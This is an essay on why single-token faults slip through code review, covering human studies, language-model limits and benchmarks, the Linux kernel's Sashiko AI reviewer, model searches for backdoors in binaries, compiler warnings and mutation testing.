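Maintainers may not be looking for this kind of fault, either. Braz and Bacchelli (2022) surveyed about 180 developers on what they focus on in code review. Although 105 of them worked on security-sensitive software, only 9 mentioned security. When asked about it directly, 111 said they always considered it. The first answers are probably a better guide to what they normally do, because the question did not mention security.

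Maintainers who knew their projects well still missed the full stop in xz and the swapped letter in curl. Both changes came from contributors with a plausible reason to make them, and familiarity with a colleague can make a reviewer less careful. We can't estimate from these cases how often maintainers catch such faults, because people hear about the failures that come to light but seldom about the faults that maintainers reject.

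The reviewers in these experiments were reading unfamiliar code, so the percentages may not apply directly to maintainers, who might catch far more than half of the one-token faults in a small change to code they know well. But unfamiliarity alone cannot explain the differences within each experiment. The people who missed the negative number were reading strangers' code under the same conditions as those who found the SQL injection, and the reviewers who saw the discount file last were no less experienced than those who saw it first. These differences could still be smaller among maintainers.

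## How language models handle a one-token difference

Language models don't get tired, so the last file in a change should give them less trouble than it gives people. They can still miss a wrong token, perhaps partly because of how they receive a text and combine information from it. Researchers have measured how well models catch such errors, mostly by testing them on correct and faulty versions of the same code.

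### What splitting text into tokens hides

Before a language model processes a text, a tokeniser splits it into tokens and replaces each with a number. Many tokenisers use *byte-pair encoding*, which starts with single characters and repeatedly merges the most common neighbouring pair. *Large Language Models* (2026), a mathematical introduction, illustrates this with the string `abcababc`. The most common pair, `ab`, becomes a new symbol, `d`, which gives `dcddc`. Then `dc` becomes `e`, which gives `ede`.

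Eight characters have become three tokens. If the last letter had been `a`, the same merges would have produced `edda`. Changing one letter therefore replaces one token with two, and the similarity between the two strings can't be seen from the token numbers.

A model has to learn during training which letters each token contains. *From Tokens To Agents* (2026) gives this as the reason models could not, until recently, count the r's in "strawberry". In *Spelling-out is not Straightforward* (2025), Llama 3 8B spelled 94% of single tokens correctly, and an older model, Amber, spelled 59% correctly. Every model tested got the first letter right more than 94% of the time but did worse on later letters. A swapped letter near the end of a long variable name may therefore be harder for a model to detect than one at the start.

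A tokeniser that groups several digits into one token can hide a single digit in the same way. This problem affects operators less, because `=` and `==` usually have separate tokens. When a model fails to detect a missing equals sign, it has normally received a different token but not used it.

### How one token can get lost in an average

A transformer combines information from different positions roughly as follows:

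1. It turns each token into a list of numbers and adds a second list that represents the token's position.
2. For each position, it scores how relevant the other positions are and converts the scores into weights that add up to 1.
3. It uses these weights to average the information from all those positions, and a small network processes the result.
4. It repeats steps 2 and 3 in each further layer, often dozens of times, and calculates its answer from the final list of numbers.

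The weight of a token with score s is e^s divided by the sum of the same expression over all tokens. If 1,000 tokens have equal scores, each has a weight of 0.1%. Raising one token's score by 2 increases its weight to only about 0.7%. For that token to get half of the total weight, its score must be 6.9 higher than the others, or 13.8 higher in a text of a million tokens. So a model can concentrate on one token, but it must have learned to score that token well above the others, by a larger margin in longer texts.

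Hahn and Rofin cite earlier proofs that, in a simplified transformer, changing one of n input bits changes the result at any other position by an amount that shrinks in proportion to 1/n. Real transformers also rescale their internal values, which can magnify tiny differences. For example, they easily learn to report only the first bit of a string, because the bit that matters is always in the same position.

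An early experiment fits the idea that a fault is harder to find when more text surrounds it. In *Bug In the Code Stack* (2024), models had to find one small bug in increasing amounts of code. Claude 3 Opus was right 84% of the time with 500 tokens of code and 18% with 16,000. GPT-4o fell only from 82% to 74%, so a large drop was not inevitable, even for models that are now obsolete.

### Why some functions are hard to learn

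The extreme case is parity, where changing any bit changes the answer. A transformer can compute parity in principle, but in practice training rarely produces one that does so on long inputs. Hahn and Rofin explain this through the model's parameters, the numbers that training adjusts. They asked how much a model's answers change if someone shifts its parameters very slightly in a random direction. With the two possible answers coded as +1 and −1, they proved that for very long inputs:

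average squared change ≥ (average sensitivity ÷ n) − a small term

The small term shrinks as the model's lists of numbers get longer. For parity, average sensitivity is n, so the right-hand side is close to 1. The squared change would be 1 if the shifted model answered 0 to every input, which carries no information. For a majority vote, average sensitivity divided by n is about 0.18 at 21 bits and 0.008 at 10,001 bits, and keeps falling towards zero as the number of bits grows.

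A transformer that computes parity on long inputs has to magnify tiny differences enormously, and a slight change in its parameters disrupts this. The parameter settings that work form a *sharp minimum*, a tiny region of low error surrounded by high error. Training adjusts the parameters in small steps and seldom reaches it. When Hahn and Rofin trained models on strings of 4 to 30 bits, the minimum for parity became steadily sharper as the strings got longer. For majority and two other functions, sharpness was orders of magnitude lower and barely rose with length.

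In another experiment, models trained on part of a random function of 10 bits filled in the remaining answers. The completed functions were less sensitive than the true ones, meaning the models too often gave the same answer for strings that differ by one bit. A similar bias would be unhelpful in a reviewer, since a correct program and its faulty copy also differ by only one token.

However, finding a wrong operator differs from computing parity. Deciding whether all 21 bits are ones has an average sensitivity close to zero, so the theorem predicts no difficulty. As Amiri and colleagues point out, a transformer can do it by looking for a zero with a single *attention head*, the part that calculates one set of weights. An obviously wrong operator resembles that zero. An operator that is wrong only because it contradicts a comment or a later line is harder to find, because the model must connect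 several parts of the text, but it still doesn't have to combine every token.

The theorem has other limits. It describes what happens as input length grows without bound, and it covers transformers that process text in both directions, whereas most chat models process it from left to right. It also describes the parameter settings that solve a task, not how training reaches them.

A task may not be hard for a language model to learn just because its answer depends on one token. In *Language Models, Graph Searching, and Supervision Adulteration*, Frydenlund (2025) studied a task in which several paths lead out from one point in a graph and the model must produce the path that ends at a named target. The target's name is a single token that determines the correct path. Models trained in the standard way only guessed, but hiding some of the earlier tokens during training let them learn the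 task on small graphs. Frydenlund found little empirical support for an earlier conjecture that the models failed because the answer depended on one token.

### Why written steps help

Parity becomes easy if a model can write down intermediate results. For the string 1011, it can write 1, 1, 0, 1, where each digit records whether the number of ones so far is odd. Each step depends only on the previous result and the next bit, however long the string is. In Hahn and Rofin's experiments, the minimum stayed shallow even for strings of about 300 bits.

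Amiri and colleagues studied such tasks using an idealised transformer in which each attention head attends to exactly one position. They proved that the number of steps needed to compute parity, a median or the middle digit of a product grows at least in proportion to the length of the input. If a model generated far fewer steps, fixing part of the input could make every head attend only to fixed positions, and the remaining tokens could no longer affect the answer. This is impossible for parity, because changing any one of those tokens flips the answer.

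These are worst-case results, and the check for 21 ones needs no written steps. But trained models behaved similarly. On strings of up to 500 bits, they succeeded if they wrote at least about every third step. Writing rows of dots instead of the intermediate results helped much less. Small models that multiplied 12-digit binary numbers without any steps made most of their errors in the middle digits, so a wrong product could still begin and end with the correct digits.

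### Finding one changed operator

Current models rarely miss a single changed operator when they have a description of what the code should do. *RTLReviewBench* (Mahmud, 2026) tested 12 models on Verilog, a language for designing computer chips. Each model read a specification and one module and, without running the module, judged whether it was correct. For 42 designs, the test included a correct module, a copy with one operator changed, and a version with a real mistake made by a code-writing model.

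The 12 models together missed 9 of 504 changed operators (1.8%) and 28 of 504 real mistakes (5.6%). Mahmud suggests that real mistakes are harder to catch because they are in code that a model generated to look right, while a changed operator is one visible token. In the shop-discount experiment, only about half of the human reviewers reported the wrong operator, but nobody had told them to expect defects, whereas the models had to say whether the code was right.

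The models also rejected about a fifth of the correct modules. Over the full set of 114 designs, false alarm rates ranged from 2% for Claude Haiku 5.5 to 59% for GPT-4.1. The low miss rate therefore overstates how well the weaker models distinguish faulty code from correct code. But over-rejection is only part of the reason the miss rate was low, because Haiku missed only 3.5% of faulty modules and raised hardly any false alarms. Models often rejected correct code because they misapplied a Verilog rule or invented a requirement that was not in the specification.

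Whether a model wrote its verdict or its reason first made a large difference. Mahmud first asked for a verdict and then a reason, and in 15 answers the reason contradicted the verdict. Gemma 4, for instance, approved a module and then explained that the module computed the opposite of the specified operation. A model writes from left to right, so an explanation can't influence a verdict that comes before it.

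Putting the reason before the verdict raised accuracy by an average of 8 percentage points in three models that normally give short answers. Telling them to trace the logic step by step did not help if the verdict still came first. Doing both raised their accuracy by 11 to 16 points. These results are consistent with the work on parity, although the experiment did not test whether the cause is the same. A majority vote over five answers from the same model did not help, because all five agreed on over 90% of items.

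Farrag (2026), in *What Do Explanations and Fixes Add to LLM Code Review?*, found even fewer misses in short Python and Java programs with written requirements. Six current models accepted only about 1% of the faulty programs. In one of these programs, a function for finding the greatest common divisor passed its arguments on in the wrong order. Claude Haiku traced the inputs 35 and 21, found that they became 14 and 21 and then never changed, and corrected the order.

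False alarms were harder to count because some labels in the answer key were wrong. When asked only for a verdict, the models appeared to reject 10.6% of correct programs. Farrag then checked programs they had rejected and found that many were faulty. With corrected labels, the rate fell to 3.7%. A model had already identified 29 of the 39 faults confirmed in that check.

### When nobody asks for faults

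Models do worse if the question doesn't direct them to look for a fault. In *Using Mutation-Analysis to Examine an LLM's Ability to Summarize Code* (2026), Khatib, Pu and colleagues asked models to explain programs in plain English. They then made one small change to a program, asked for a new explanation and checked whether a person could identify the change by comparing the two explanations. *Mutation-based Consistency Testing for Evaluating the Code Understanding Capability of LLMs* (2024) had instead tested whether models noticed that changed code no longer matched its description.

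On 150 changes to 50 human-written programs, GPT-4's explanations revealed 49% of the changes and GPT-5.2's revealed 85%. For changed operators, the figures were 44% and 88%. Models newer than GPT-5.2 may do better, but these programs were short, and most were a single function. On another set of programs, GPT-4's results fell from 77% for single functions to 17% for programs that run several tasks at once.

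### Vulnerable and patched functions

The results are much worse for security flaws in isolated functions. Cichoń and Dmitruk (2026), in *A Function-Level Vulnerability Score Measures Flag Rate More Than the Model*, used pairs consisting of a vulnerable C or C++ function and the same function after its developers had fixed it. A model saw one function at a time and had to flag the first and clear the second. Results for three of the models on 1,000 pairs were:

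| | Both right | Flagged both | Cleared both | Both wrong |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 17.7% | 53.3% | 27.1% | 1.9% |
| GPT-5.2 | 11.1% | 81.9% | 5.1% | 1.9% |
| Grok 4.3 | 25.4% | 53.0% | 17.9% | 3.7% |
| Fair coin | 25% | 25% | 25% | 25% |

Opus did respond to some of the fixes, since it got both functions right about nine times as often as it got both wrong, whereas random guessing would do each equally often. But most of the time it gave both functions the same verdict. Of 68 models, 64 gave matching verdicts more often than they would have if they had judged the two functions independently. Their answers depended mainly on the text that the functions shared.

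Language models have made little visible progress on this test. *Vulnerability Detection with Code Language Models* (2024) found that GPT-4 did no better than guessing on such pairs. According to Cichoń and Dmitruk, GPT-4 got 12.9% of them right when it reasoned step by step, and the seven main models they tested got 7% to 18% right on a sample from the same collection.

These pairs are only partly comparable to one-token changes. Most of the fixes add code, and the models had no specification to check the code against. A function's safety can depend on the code that calls it, so some pairs can't be judged from the function alone. The models also had to give their verdict first, which Mahmud found harmful for models that do not reason beforehand. No one has measured how well people do on the same pairs.

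### Missing a difference and misjudging it

A model can give the wrong answer because it missed the difference or because it misjudged what the difference does. In the study by Khatib and colleagues, some of GPT-4's explanations failed because they were too vague to mention the changed part, and others because they described what such code normally does. When `parent[i] == i` became `parent[i] != i` in a well-known algorithm, GPT-4 still described the original condition. Another program was changed to print the label "Wallet: " without customers' wallet balances, but the explanation still mentioned the balances.

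*Evaluating Language Models on Cross-Language Code Functional Equivalence* (2026) classified cases where a model wrongly judged that two programs did the same thing. In 11 cases, the model relied on a general resemblance and never compared what the programs did. In 6, it compared them but misinterpreted the relevant behaviour.

A model's internal activity sometimes contains information about a difference that its verdict does not reflect. Cichoń and Dmitruk trained a simple classifier on the internal activity of open models as they processed vulnerable functions and their fixed versions. When the two versions were almost equal in length, the classifier typically rated the vulnerable one as more suspicious 78% of the time, compared with 64% for a classifier that used only word frequencies. For the six models they examined most closely, the written verdicts ranked the functions correctly only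 50% to 57% of the time across all pairs. But the classifier trained on internal activity did little better than chance when a fix had removed code, so it may mostly have recognised the kinds of lines that fixes add. The researchers also did not test whether the models use this information.

Giving a model both versions makes it easier to isolate the second kind of failure. In *Large Language Models for Multi-Lingual Equivalent Mutant Detection*, Shu, Tian and colleagues (2026) did this with 4,390 pairs of Java and C programs, asking models whether a small change affected behaviour. The models were mostly small. Those with extra training on this task did better than those given only instructions, so training can improve a model's ability to judge a change's effect.

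A correct verdict can also rest on faulty reasoning. *EquiBench* (2025) used 2,400 pairs of programs, half of them equivalent, and allowed only "Yes" or "No" as an answer. *Assessing LLM Program Reasoning through Equivalence Proofs* (Wang, Miltner and Chen, 2026) also required a machine-checkable proof. Each of the five models it tested reached the right verdict on at least 66% of the tasks, but the share of proofs that passed the check on the first attempt ranged from 36% to 94%. All 200 of its pairs were equivalent, so the verdicts alone are weak evidence of how well models spot differences.

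In one pair, both programs calculated a row of pixels, but one reset two variables after each pixel and the other reset them before the next. Opus 5.5 noted the different timing and correctly judged the programs equivalent. But it also claimed in its explanation that the variables always matched at the start of the loop. In one run, they were 0 and 0 at that point in one program and 5 and 0 in the other. Wang and colleagues asked models to check individual claims like this, and the models accepted 27 of the 411 that an automatic solver had shown to be false.

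Explanations of real faults are usually better than this. In *Are LLMs Reliable Code Reviewers?* (2026), when older models correctly rejected a program, they described the symptoms correctly at least 91% of the time but named the right type of bug only 38% to 75% of the time. When Farrag repeated that study with newer models, other models judged that 99.5% of the explanations pointed to the planted fault. In Mahmud's test, 94% of correct rejections cited the real defect. The weakest model, Llama 3.3 70B, flagged 74% of the faulty modules but correctly explained the fault in only 41%.

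## AI reviewers on real code and hidden backdoors

Most tests of language models use short programs or single functions. On a real project, an AI reviewer has to judge a change to a large program and work out which other parts of the code matter. Linux kernel developers have tried this in public since March 2026. A February 2026 benchmark tested models on the harder task of finding backdoors in compiled programs without the source code.

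### How an automatic review works

The kernel's AI reviewer is called Sashiko. Gushchin (2026), in *Introduce Sashiko (agentic review of Linux kernel changes)*, presented it as a system that reviews every *patch*, or proposed change, sent to the kernel's main mailing list and several others. Gushchin works for Google, which provides the computing power, and at launch Sashiko used Google's Gemini 3.1 Pro model. The Linux Foundation now owns the project. According to the Linux Foundation's *sashiko 0.2.5*, a review goes roughly as follows:

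1. Sashiko takes the patch from the mailing list and applies it to a copy of the kernel's source code.
2. It sends the model the patch, general instructions and notes on the part of the kernel that the patch changes. The model may also get whole files and earlier changes, which help it work out what the surrounding code does.
3. The model examines the patch seven times, looking for different problems each time: a flawed design, code that doesn't match the author's description, errors in the flow of execution, misuse of memory, clashes between parts of the program that run at once, security holes, and mistakes in controlling hardware.
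4. It merges findings that describe the same problem.
5. It compares the remaining concerns with those it dismissed along the way, and keeps only the ones that hold up against the code.
6. It checks these again, removes false alarms and estimates how serious each problem is.
7. It writes up the results as an email, with comments beside the relevant lines.

The execution-flow check explicitly covers off-by-one errors, such as the `>` that should have been `>=` in the shop-discount experiment. Comparing the code with the author's description could catch the same error if the description gave the right limit. But a misleading description of a change can make errors less likely to be caught.

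*Re: Stop false review statements* (2026), a message on the kernel list, reports that reviews with Gemini 3.1 Pro used an average of 3.5 million tokens per patch. It explains that current models are poor at looking for several kinds of problem at once, and that examining the patch repeatedly has measurably improved the reviews.

### Bugs that people had already missed

When kernel developers fix a bug, they usually add a line beginning "Fixes:" that names the earlier change that caused it. Gushchin used these lines to collect 1,000 recent bugs, without excluding any that looked too hard, and Sashiko found 53% of them. A couple of months earlier, the figure had been in the low 30s. Gushchin attributes the improvement to better models, better instructions and changes to the review process.

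The Linux Foundation suggests that Sashiko is in some sense already above the human level, because human reviewers had missed all 1,000 bugs. That comparison is unfair to the humans, because the collection included only bugs they had missed. Suppose reviewers catch 80 of every 100 bugs. An AI reviewer that finds 53% of the other 20 would raise the total to about 91, a large improvement, but nobody would know how many of the first 80 it would have found by itself. The result is good evidence for using Sashiko alongside human reviewers, but little evidence about how well it would work alone.

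The collection also contains only bugs that somebody later noticed and fixed, so a well-hidden backdoor would not be in it. It mixes faults of every size, and Gushchin points out that some, such as performance problems, are very hard or impossible to see in the code. Wrong operators are visible in the code, so Sashiko may find more than 53% of them, but the experiment has no separate figure for them.

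Sashiko can also find a bug in one run and miss it in the next run on the same patch. A review with no comments is therefore weaker evidence that a patch is sound than compiling without errors is that the code is valid C.

### The dispute over noise

The value of the 53% also depends on how many of Sashiko's other comments are wrong. The Linux Foundation puts the share of wrong reports well within 20%, based on a limited number of manual checks, and considers most of the wrong ones borderline. The share of clean patches that receive a false report is a different figure, and measuring it would take a set of patches known to be correct. Gushchin asked for such a set, but Lorenzo Stoakes (2026), in *Re: Introduce Sashiko*, doubted that perfect changes exist in the kernel.

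Stoakes, who helps maintain the kernel's memory-management code, estimated that about half of Sashiko's comments on one set of patches were noise. The other half had led to several corrections, and Stoakes called the tool already very useful.

LWN's *The role of LLMs in patch review* (2026) describes how a discussion of a routine clean-up, posted on 19 March, turned into a dispute over the review process when it looked as if patch authors would have to answer Sashiko's feedback. Andrew Morton, the memory-management maintainer, planned to hold back patches until their authors had resolved or convincingly refuted every question Sashiko raised.

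Morton supported the plan by counting authors' replies to emails that mentioned Sashiko. In 22 cases the author agreed that the patch needed changes, in 2 the author disagreed, and 1 reply was unclear. Another 10 to 15 emails had no reply yet. Stoakes responded that 22 out of 35 is only 63%, and that a review counted as a success if just one of its comments was right. Stoakes estimated that about half of the individual comments were valid.

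These figures conflict less than they appear to. If a review has three comments, each with an independent 50% chance of being right, the chance that at least one is right is 1 − 0.5^3, or 87.5%. That is close to Morton's 22 successes out of 25 replies, or 88%. An author may well welcome such a review because it improves the patch, but someone still has to work out which comments to ignore.

That work was Stoakes's main concern. Some reports were so complicated that only an expert could tell whether they mattered, and the experts were already overworked. New contributors might rewrite a patch several times to address *hallucinations*, problems the model had made up. Each new version could attract new comments, so a patch might never be finished. Stoakes also pointed out that human reviewers tend to get more reliable over time, and that no human reviewer in memory management in memory had a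 record as poor as 50%. Stoakes wanted the maintainers of each area to use Sashiko as an aid and focus on the reports it rated as serious.

Gushchin agreed that nobody should have to address every point but thought it reasonable to require answers to the serious ones. Gushchin also defended some noise in principle, giving the example of a system that found every bug but was wrong in 20% of its reports. Most projects would probably accept that. Chris Mason, who wrote the instructions on which Sashiko is based, had at first strongly favoured avoiding false alarms, and Gushchin believed this had caused some real bugs to be missed. *CR-Bench* (2026), a benchmark for AI code reviewers, describes the same trade-off, in which reviewers designed to find every hidden problem can produce so much noise that the real problems are hard to spot.

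Two months later, maintainers still disagreed about how often Sashiko's reports were correct. Kozlowski (2026), in *Stop false review statements*, estimated that 80–90% of them were false. Guenter Roeck, another maintainer, replied that 80–90% of the ones Roeck had seen were correct. Matthew Brost had put the success rate for graphics code at about half, and added that even the wrong comments helped by raising questions about the assumptions behind a patch.

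Apart from Morton's tally, these are impressions, and people may be more likely to remember the comments that annoyed them. But the tool may also work much better in some parts of the kernel than in others, since Gushchin said that only some had good specialised instructions. Maintainers also disagree about whether a correct comment on a trivial matter counts as a false report.

Even a correct comment may have little to do with the patch. bexelbie (2026), in *What's Actually in a Sashiko Review?*, used a program to sort 466 findings by the phrases they contained. About 72% concerned the patch, 12% concerned its effect on existing code, and 9% concerned older bugs nearby. The older bugs were concentrated in 19% of the reviews, where they took up 28% of the text on average. People who submitted those patches had to read, and perhaps respond to, comments about bugs they had not introduced. bexelbie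 suspected that Sashiko might keep reporting the same old bugs to different people, but found almost no repetition. The analysis did not check whether any of the findings were correct.

The findings about a patch's effect on existing code were the longest, averaging 103 words, because they also had to describe that code. They are probably also the most useful when the decisive change looks fine by itself and is wrong only because of something in another file. A person reading the diff would have to think to open that file.

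Kozlowski objected mainly to Sashiko sending an email with a "Reviewed-by" line. Kernel developers use that line to vouch for a patch, and Kozlowski argued that only a person can do that. Roeck knew of no rule against Sashiko using the line, and had come to trust its reviews significantly more than human ones because it had found bugs in patches that already had a person's "Reviewed-by" line. Laurent Pinchart, another participant in the discussion, would not treat a model's approval as a sign that a patch was ready. A person's approval can also mislead, as it did with the full stop in xz.

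Kernel developers kept using AI review despite the critics. Ferreira (2026) reported in *Linus Torvalds rebukes anti-AI stances in the Linux kernel code review process* that Torvalds defended it in July, in a dispute set off by Sashiko, and called AI a clearly useful tool. In November, Gushchin and Brewer (2026) argued in *Lessons from building Sashiko, an agentic code review system* that reviewing code had always limited the speed of large open-source projects more than writing it had. If so, using AI to write patches faster will only lengthen the review queue and increase the pressure to automate some of the reviewing.

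### Does it help to use several models?

Some kernel developers now run several leading models on every patch to weed out invented problems. Jakub Kicinski announced this in August and said they had a budget for using Meta's models, according to Posch (2026) in *Linux Kernel Drops AI Tag Requirement, Uses Meta AI For Code Reviews*.

The benefit depends on how people combine the answers. Suppose two models each have a hit rate of 60% and a false alarm rate of 10%, and their mistakes are independent. Accepting a report from either model raises the hit rate to 84% and the false alarm rate to 19%. Accepting only what both report lowers the false alarm rate to 1% and the hit rate to 36%. The second method better fits Kicinski's aim of filtering out invented problems. It would reduce the noise that Stoakes complained about, but it could discard a real fault that only one model reported.

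Real models' mistakes are unlikely to be independent, because the models learn from much of the same text. The student auditors' mistakes at Rice were not independent either. Different models should agree less often than the five answers from a single model did in Mahmud's test, but it is not clear by how much.

Public evidence on this is thin. Smith (2026), in *Three AI Models Scanned the Same Code. Their Bug Lists Barely Overlapped*, gives a seemingly promising example, but each model may have found real bugs that the others missed, or each may have raised its own false alarms. Checking the individual reports would show which. A fair test would also compare three different models with three runs of the best one, because Sashiko's findings vary between runs and repetition alone should find some extra bugs.

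### What people do with an automatic review

In most projects a person still makes the final decision, so it matters how an automatic review affects that person's reading. In *Deep Learning-based Code Reviews*, Tufano, Martin-Lopez and colleagues (2024) had 29 experts review programs with or without an automatically generated review as a starting point. The experts accepted most of the model's comments as valid and tended to look where it had commented instead of searching the rest of the code.

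Experts who started from an automatic review reported a larger number of minor problems than those who worked alone, but not a larger number of serious ones. They did not save time and were no more confident in the result.

This result is dated, because the models of 2024 were much weaker reviewers than today's. Better comments would presumably lead people to more of the serious problems. But people might still look mainly where the comments point, and may do so even more if they trust the tool. A wrong token that the model misses would then get less human attention than it would without the model. A simple precaution is for the person to read the patch before opening the automatic review, although the review then saves no time.

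### Looking for backdoors without the source code

All of these reviewers had source code, and usually a diff. Many people who run a program have neither. A compiler discards comments and most names, and rearranges operations to make the program faster. A reader of the compiled file therefore can't compare a condition with the comment above it, as reviewers could in the shop-discount experiment. Without a trusted older copy, the reader can't run a diff either.

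In *We hid backdoors in ~40 MB binaries*, Grabowski, Strzaliński and colleagues (2026) tested how well language models find backdoors in compiled programs. The software company Quesma owns their benchmark, BinaryAudit, and has published the tasks so that others can repeat the test. The researchers added backdoors by hand to four open-source network programs, including a web server and a program for logging in to remote computers. They then compiled the programs and removed the information that normally helps programmers navigate a compiled file.

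The models could use Ghidra and Radare2, two free tools that turn compiled instructions back into rough C. To pass, a model usually had to report that the file had a backdoor and give the location of the right function. In a few tasks, it got three files and only had to name the ones with backdoors. These tasks were no easier, though the researchers had expected them to be.

Claude Opus 4.6 had the best result in the researchers' report, at 49%. They had not tried hard to hide the backdoors and thought a skilled person could find them relatively easily, though they did not test any people. The added code was often about a dozen lines in a file with hundreds or thousands of functions, which is a very small change but still much larger than one token.

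In one successful search, Claude Opus 4.5 found a backdoor in the web server within five minutes. It first looked for suspicious words in the file and its 26 supporting libraries, without success. Then it listed the outside functions that each library used and found that one library could run system commands. It traced this ability to a single function, translated it into rough C and saw that it ran whatever command arrived in a certain part of a web request. Finally, it confirmed that the server used the function. The function's name had survived in the file and mentioned debugging, which made it look suspicious and may have made the search easier.

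In another program, Opus 4.6 found the function containing the backdoor but judged it safe. The function ran a system command, which the model took for a legitimate feature because the program does sometimes run scripts. The model never checked where the command came from, which was a message that anyone on the network could send. Unlike McVoy, who also failed to recognise a backdoor at first, the model had no trusted version to compare the code with.

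Other searches failed earlier because some models picked functions to examine more or less at random, or spent all their effort on harmless libraries and never reached the backdoor. An experienced analyst would start with the parts of the program that handle data from outside, because that is where an attacker could get in.

The models also reported backdoors in clean files 28% of the time. For example, Gemini 3 Pro reported that an attacker could run commands through a setting that controls how long a server stores information. The source code shows that the program reads this setting as a number and never runs it as a command. Without the source code, an expert can take a long time to refute a false report like this.

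Quesma's online ranking, *Can AI find backdoors in raw machine code?*, includes results for further models:

| Model | Backdoors found | False alarms on clean files |
|---|---|---|
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 49% | 17% |
| GPT-5.2-Codex, highest effort setting | 46% | 0% |

The effort setting, which controls how much a model reasons before it answers, greatly affected how many backdoors the models found. GPT-5.2-Codex found only 9% without the highest setting. GPT-5.4 went from 2% to 18% with more effort, so a later version did not guarantee a better score. These models all date from early 2026 or before, and today's may do far better.

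The tools also limit the results. The free ones could not handle programs written in Go, so the researchers excluded those programs. In one trial, Ghidra took 40 minutes to load a 50-megabyte web server and then translated it incorrectly, while the commercial tool IDA Pro loaded it in five minutes and produced usable code. A model with better tools might therefore find more backdoors without being better at recognising them.

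Grabowski and colleagues want a false alarm rate below 0.001% for practical use, because nearly all software is clean. If 10 out of 100,000 programs contained a backdoor, scanning them all at Gemini 3.1 Pro's rates would find about 5 backdoors and raise about 17,000 false alarms. A rate of 0.001% would produce about one false alarm. GPT-5.2-Codex raised none in the test, but the benchmark has only 33 tasks, and not all of them use clean files. Even 30 clean files without a false alarm would be compatible with a true rate of up to about 10%.

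## Compiler rules, tests and mutation analysis

Human and AI reviewers can read a wrong token and still approve it. Some automatic checks avoid this problem because they don't depend on anyone's judgement of the text. A compiler can reject a program that breaks a rule, and a test can run the program and compare its result with the right answer.

### Rules that reject a slip

The missing equals sign in `if (value = 100)` is dangerous in C because C accepts a number as a condition. Java requires a condition to be true or false, so the line doesn't compile if `value` is a number. Rust rejects it for a similar reason, and Python doesn't allow an ordinary assignment inside a condition. A programmer using Java, Rust or Python therefore learns about the typo within seconds.

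An assignment inside a condition is valid C, so a C compiler has to accept it, but most can warn about it. Programmers who assign there on purpose can turn off GCC's warning by putting an extra pair of parentheses around the assignment. The assignment in the 2003 kernel backdoor was in parentheses, so GCC would not have warned about it. A project can catch such cases by forbidding all assignments in conditions, but it then has to rewrite the deliberate ones.

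Type checks catch a token that produces the wrong type of value, but they can't catch `>` in place of `>=` because both operators return true or false.

Another approach is to use a smaller language. Ka-Ping Yee wrote Pvote in Pthin, a subset of Python, so that reviewers had fewer language features to understand. The program could still contain logic errors, and the expert reviewers missed Pvote's hard bug.

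A famous mistake by Apple led to a new compiler warning. Red Hat's *GCC 6 -Wmisleading-indentation vs goto fail* (2016) shows the faulty lines, from the code that Apple's operating system used to make secure connections:

```
if ((err = SSLHashSHA1.update(&hashCtx, &signedParams)) != 0)
    goto fail;
    goto fail;
```

The third line is a three-token duplicate. Without braces, an `if` in C controls only the next statement, so the first `goto fail` runs only after an error, but the second always runs. It jumps past the remaining checks to the end of the function, which returns `err`. No step has failed at that point, so `err` is 0, which means success. Apple's software therefore accepted invalid certificates, the digital documents that websites use to prove their identity. The flaw became known as "goto fail" in 2014.

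The indentation makes the duplicate look like part of the `if`. In *Proposed new warning*, Malcolm (2015), a developer at Red Hat, suggested that GCC should warn programmers whenever the indentation implies a different structure from the one GCC parses. GCC 6 included the warning the following year.

Like AI reviewers, the new rule produced some unhelpful warnings. According to *Some real-life feedback on -Wmisleading-indentation* (2016), on the GCC mailing list, it gave about four dozen warnings on Wine, a program for running Windows software on other systems. Some pointed to possible bugs and others only to odd formatting. Another developer, Antonio Diaz Diaz, got warnings in four projects about code that seemed fine, and asked the GCC team to remove the rule from the compiler's standard set. Malcolm's reply is in *Please, take '-Wmisleading-indentation' out of -Wall* (2016).

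The rule is still in the standard set. Its false alarms take less work to handle than an AI reviewer's, because the compiler gives the same warning every time and a programmer can usually remove it permanently by fixing the indentation.

### Mutation analysis

A test could also have exposed Apple's mistake, but only if it presented an invalid signature, because software with the extra line handled valid ones correctly. Developers therefore need to know whether their tests include the cases that would expose such mistakes.

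The usual measure is *line coverage*, the share of a program's lines that the tests run. It is easy to calculate, but running a line is not the same as checking it. *Mutation analysis* measures the checking more directly. It starts with a program that passes all its tests and goes as follows:

1. Make a copy of the program with one small change, such as `>=` replaced by `>`. This copy is a *mutant*.
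2. Run the tests on the mutant.
3. If at least one test fails, the tests have *killed* the mutant. If they all pass, the mutant *survives*.
4. Repeat this for many different changes and count the results.

mutation score = killed ÷ (total − equivalent)

An *equivalent* mutant behaves exactly like the original program, so no test can kill it. Suppose a loop counts `i` up from 0 in steps of 1 while `i < 10`. Changing the condition to `i != 10` makes no difference, because the loop stops at 10 either way.

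As an example, take a function that decides whether somebody is an adult by testing `age >= 18`. The table compares it with four mutants for ages in whole years:

| Condition | Age 10 | Age 17 | Age 18 | Age 30 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `age >= 18` (original) | false | false | true | true |
| `age > 18` | false | false | false | true |
| `age >= 17` | false | true | true | true |
| `age == 18` | false | false | true | false |
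| `age < 18` | true | true | false | false |

Tests for ages 10 and 30 kill the last two mutants, giving a score of 50%. The mutant `age > 18` survives because it gives a different result from the original only at 18. A test for 18 raises the score to 75%, and another for 17 raises it to 100%. Line coverage couldn't have revealed the gap, because a single test for age 30 already runs the function's only line.

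A surviving mutant that isn't equivalent marks a place where one small change would alter the program's behavior without failing any test. The mutation score therefore describes the tests more than the program. In the experiment by Schulte and colleagues, the random edits that passed every test were also surviving mutants, whether equivalent or not.

No general method can decide whether two programs are equivalent, so the mutation score is uncertain. *Mutation-Guided LLM-based Test Generation at Meta* (Foster, Harper and colleagues, 2025) puts the usual share of equivalent mutants at 10–15% for tools that make changes by fixed rules. If tests kill 80 of 100 mutants, that range would mean a score between 89% and 94%, but someone would have to examine the 20 survivors to determine the actual score.

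### Showing mutants to reviewers at Google

Running all the tests on every possible mutant takes a lot of computing power. Meta's *LLMs Are the Key to Mutation Testing and Better Compliance* (2025) lists this as an obstacle for large companies, along with the time developers spend on mutants that don't resemble any serious fault. Google already runs more than 500 million tests a day on unmutated code.

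Google's solution is to create mutants only in newly changed lines that the tests run, with at most one mutant per line. Up to seven surviving mutants per file appear in the code review. A reviewer can ask the author to add a test, and the author can mark a mutant as not useful. Most of the system's mutation types alter a single operator, such as by swapping one comparison for another, but one type removes a whole block of statements. *Practical Mutation Testing at Scale* (2021) reports that developers saw about 2 million of the almost 17 million mutants in 760,000 changes.

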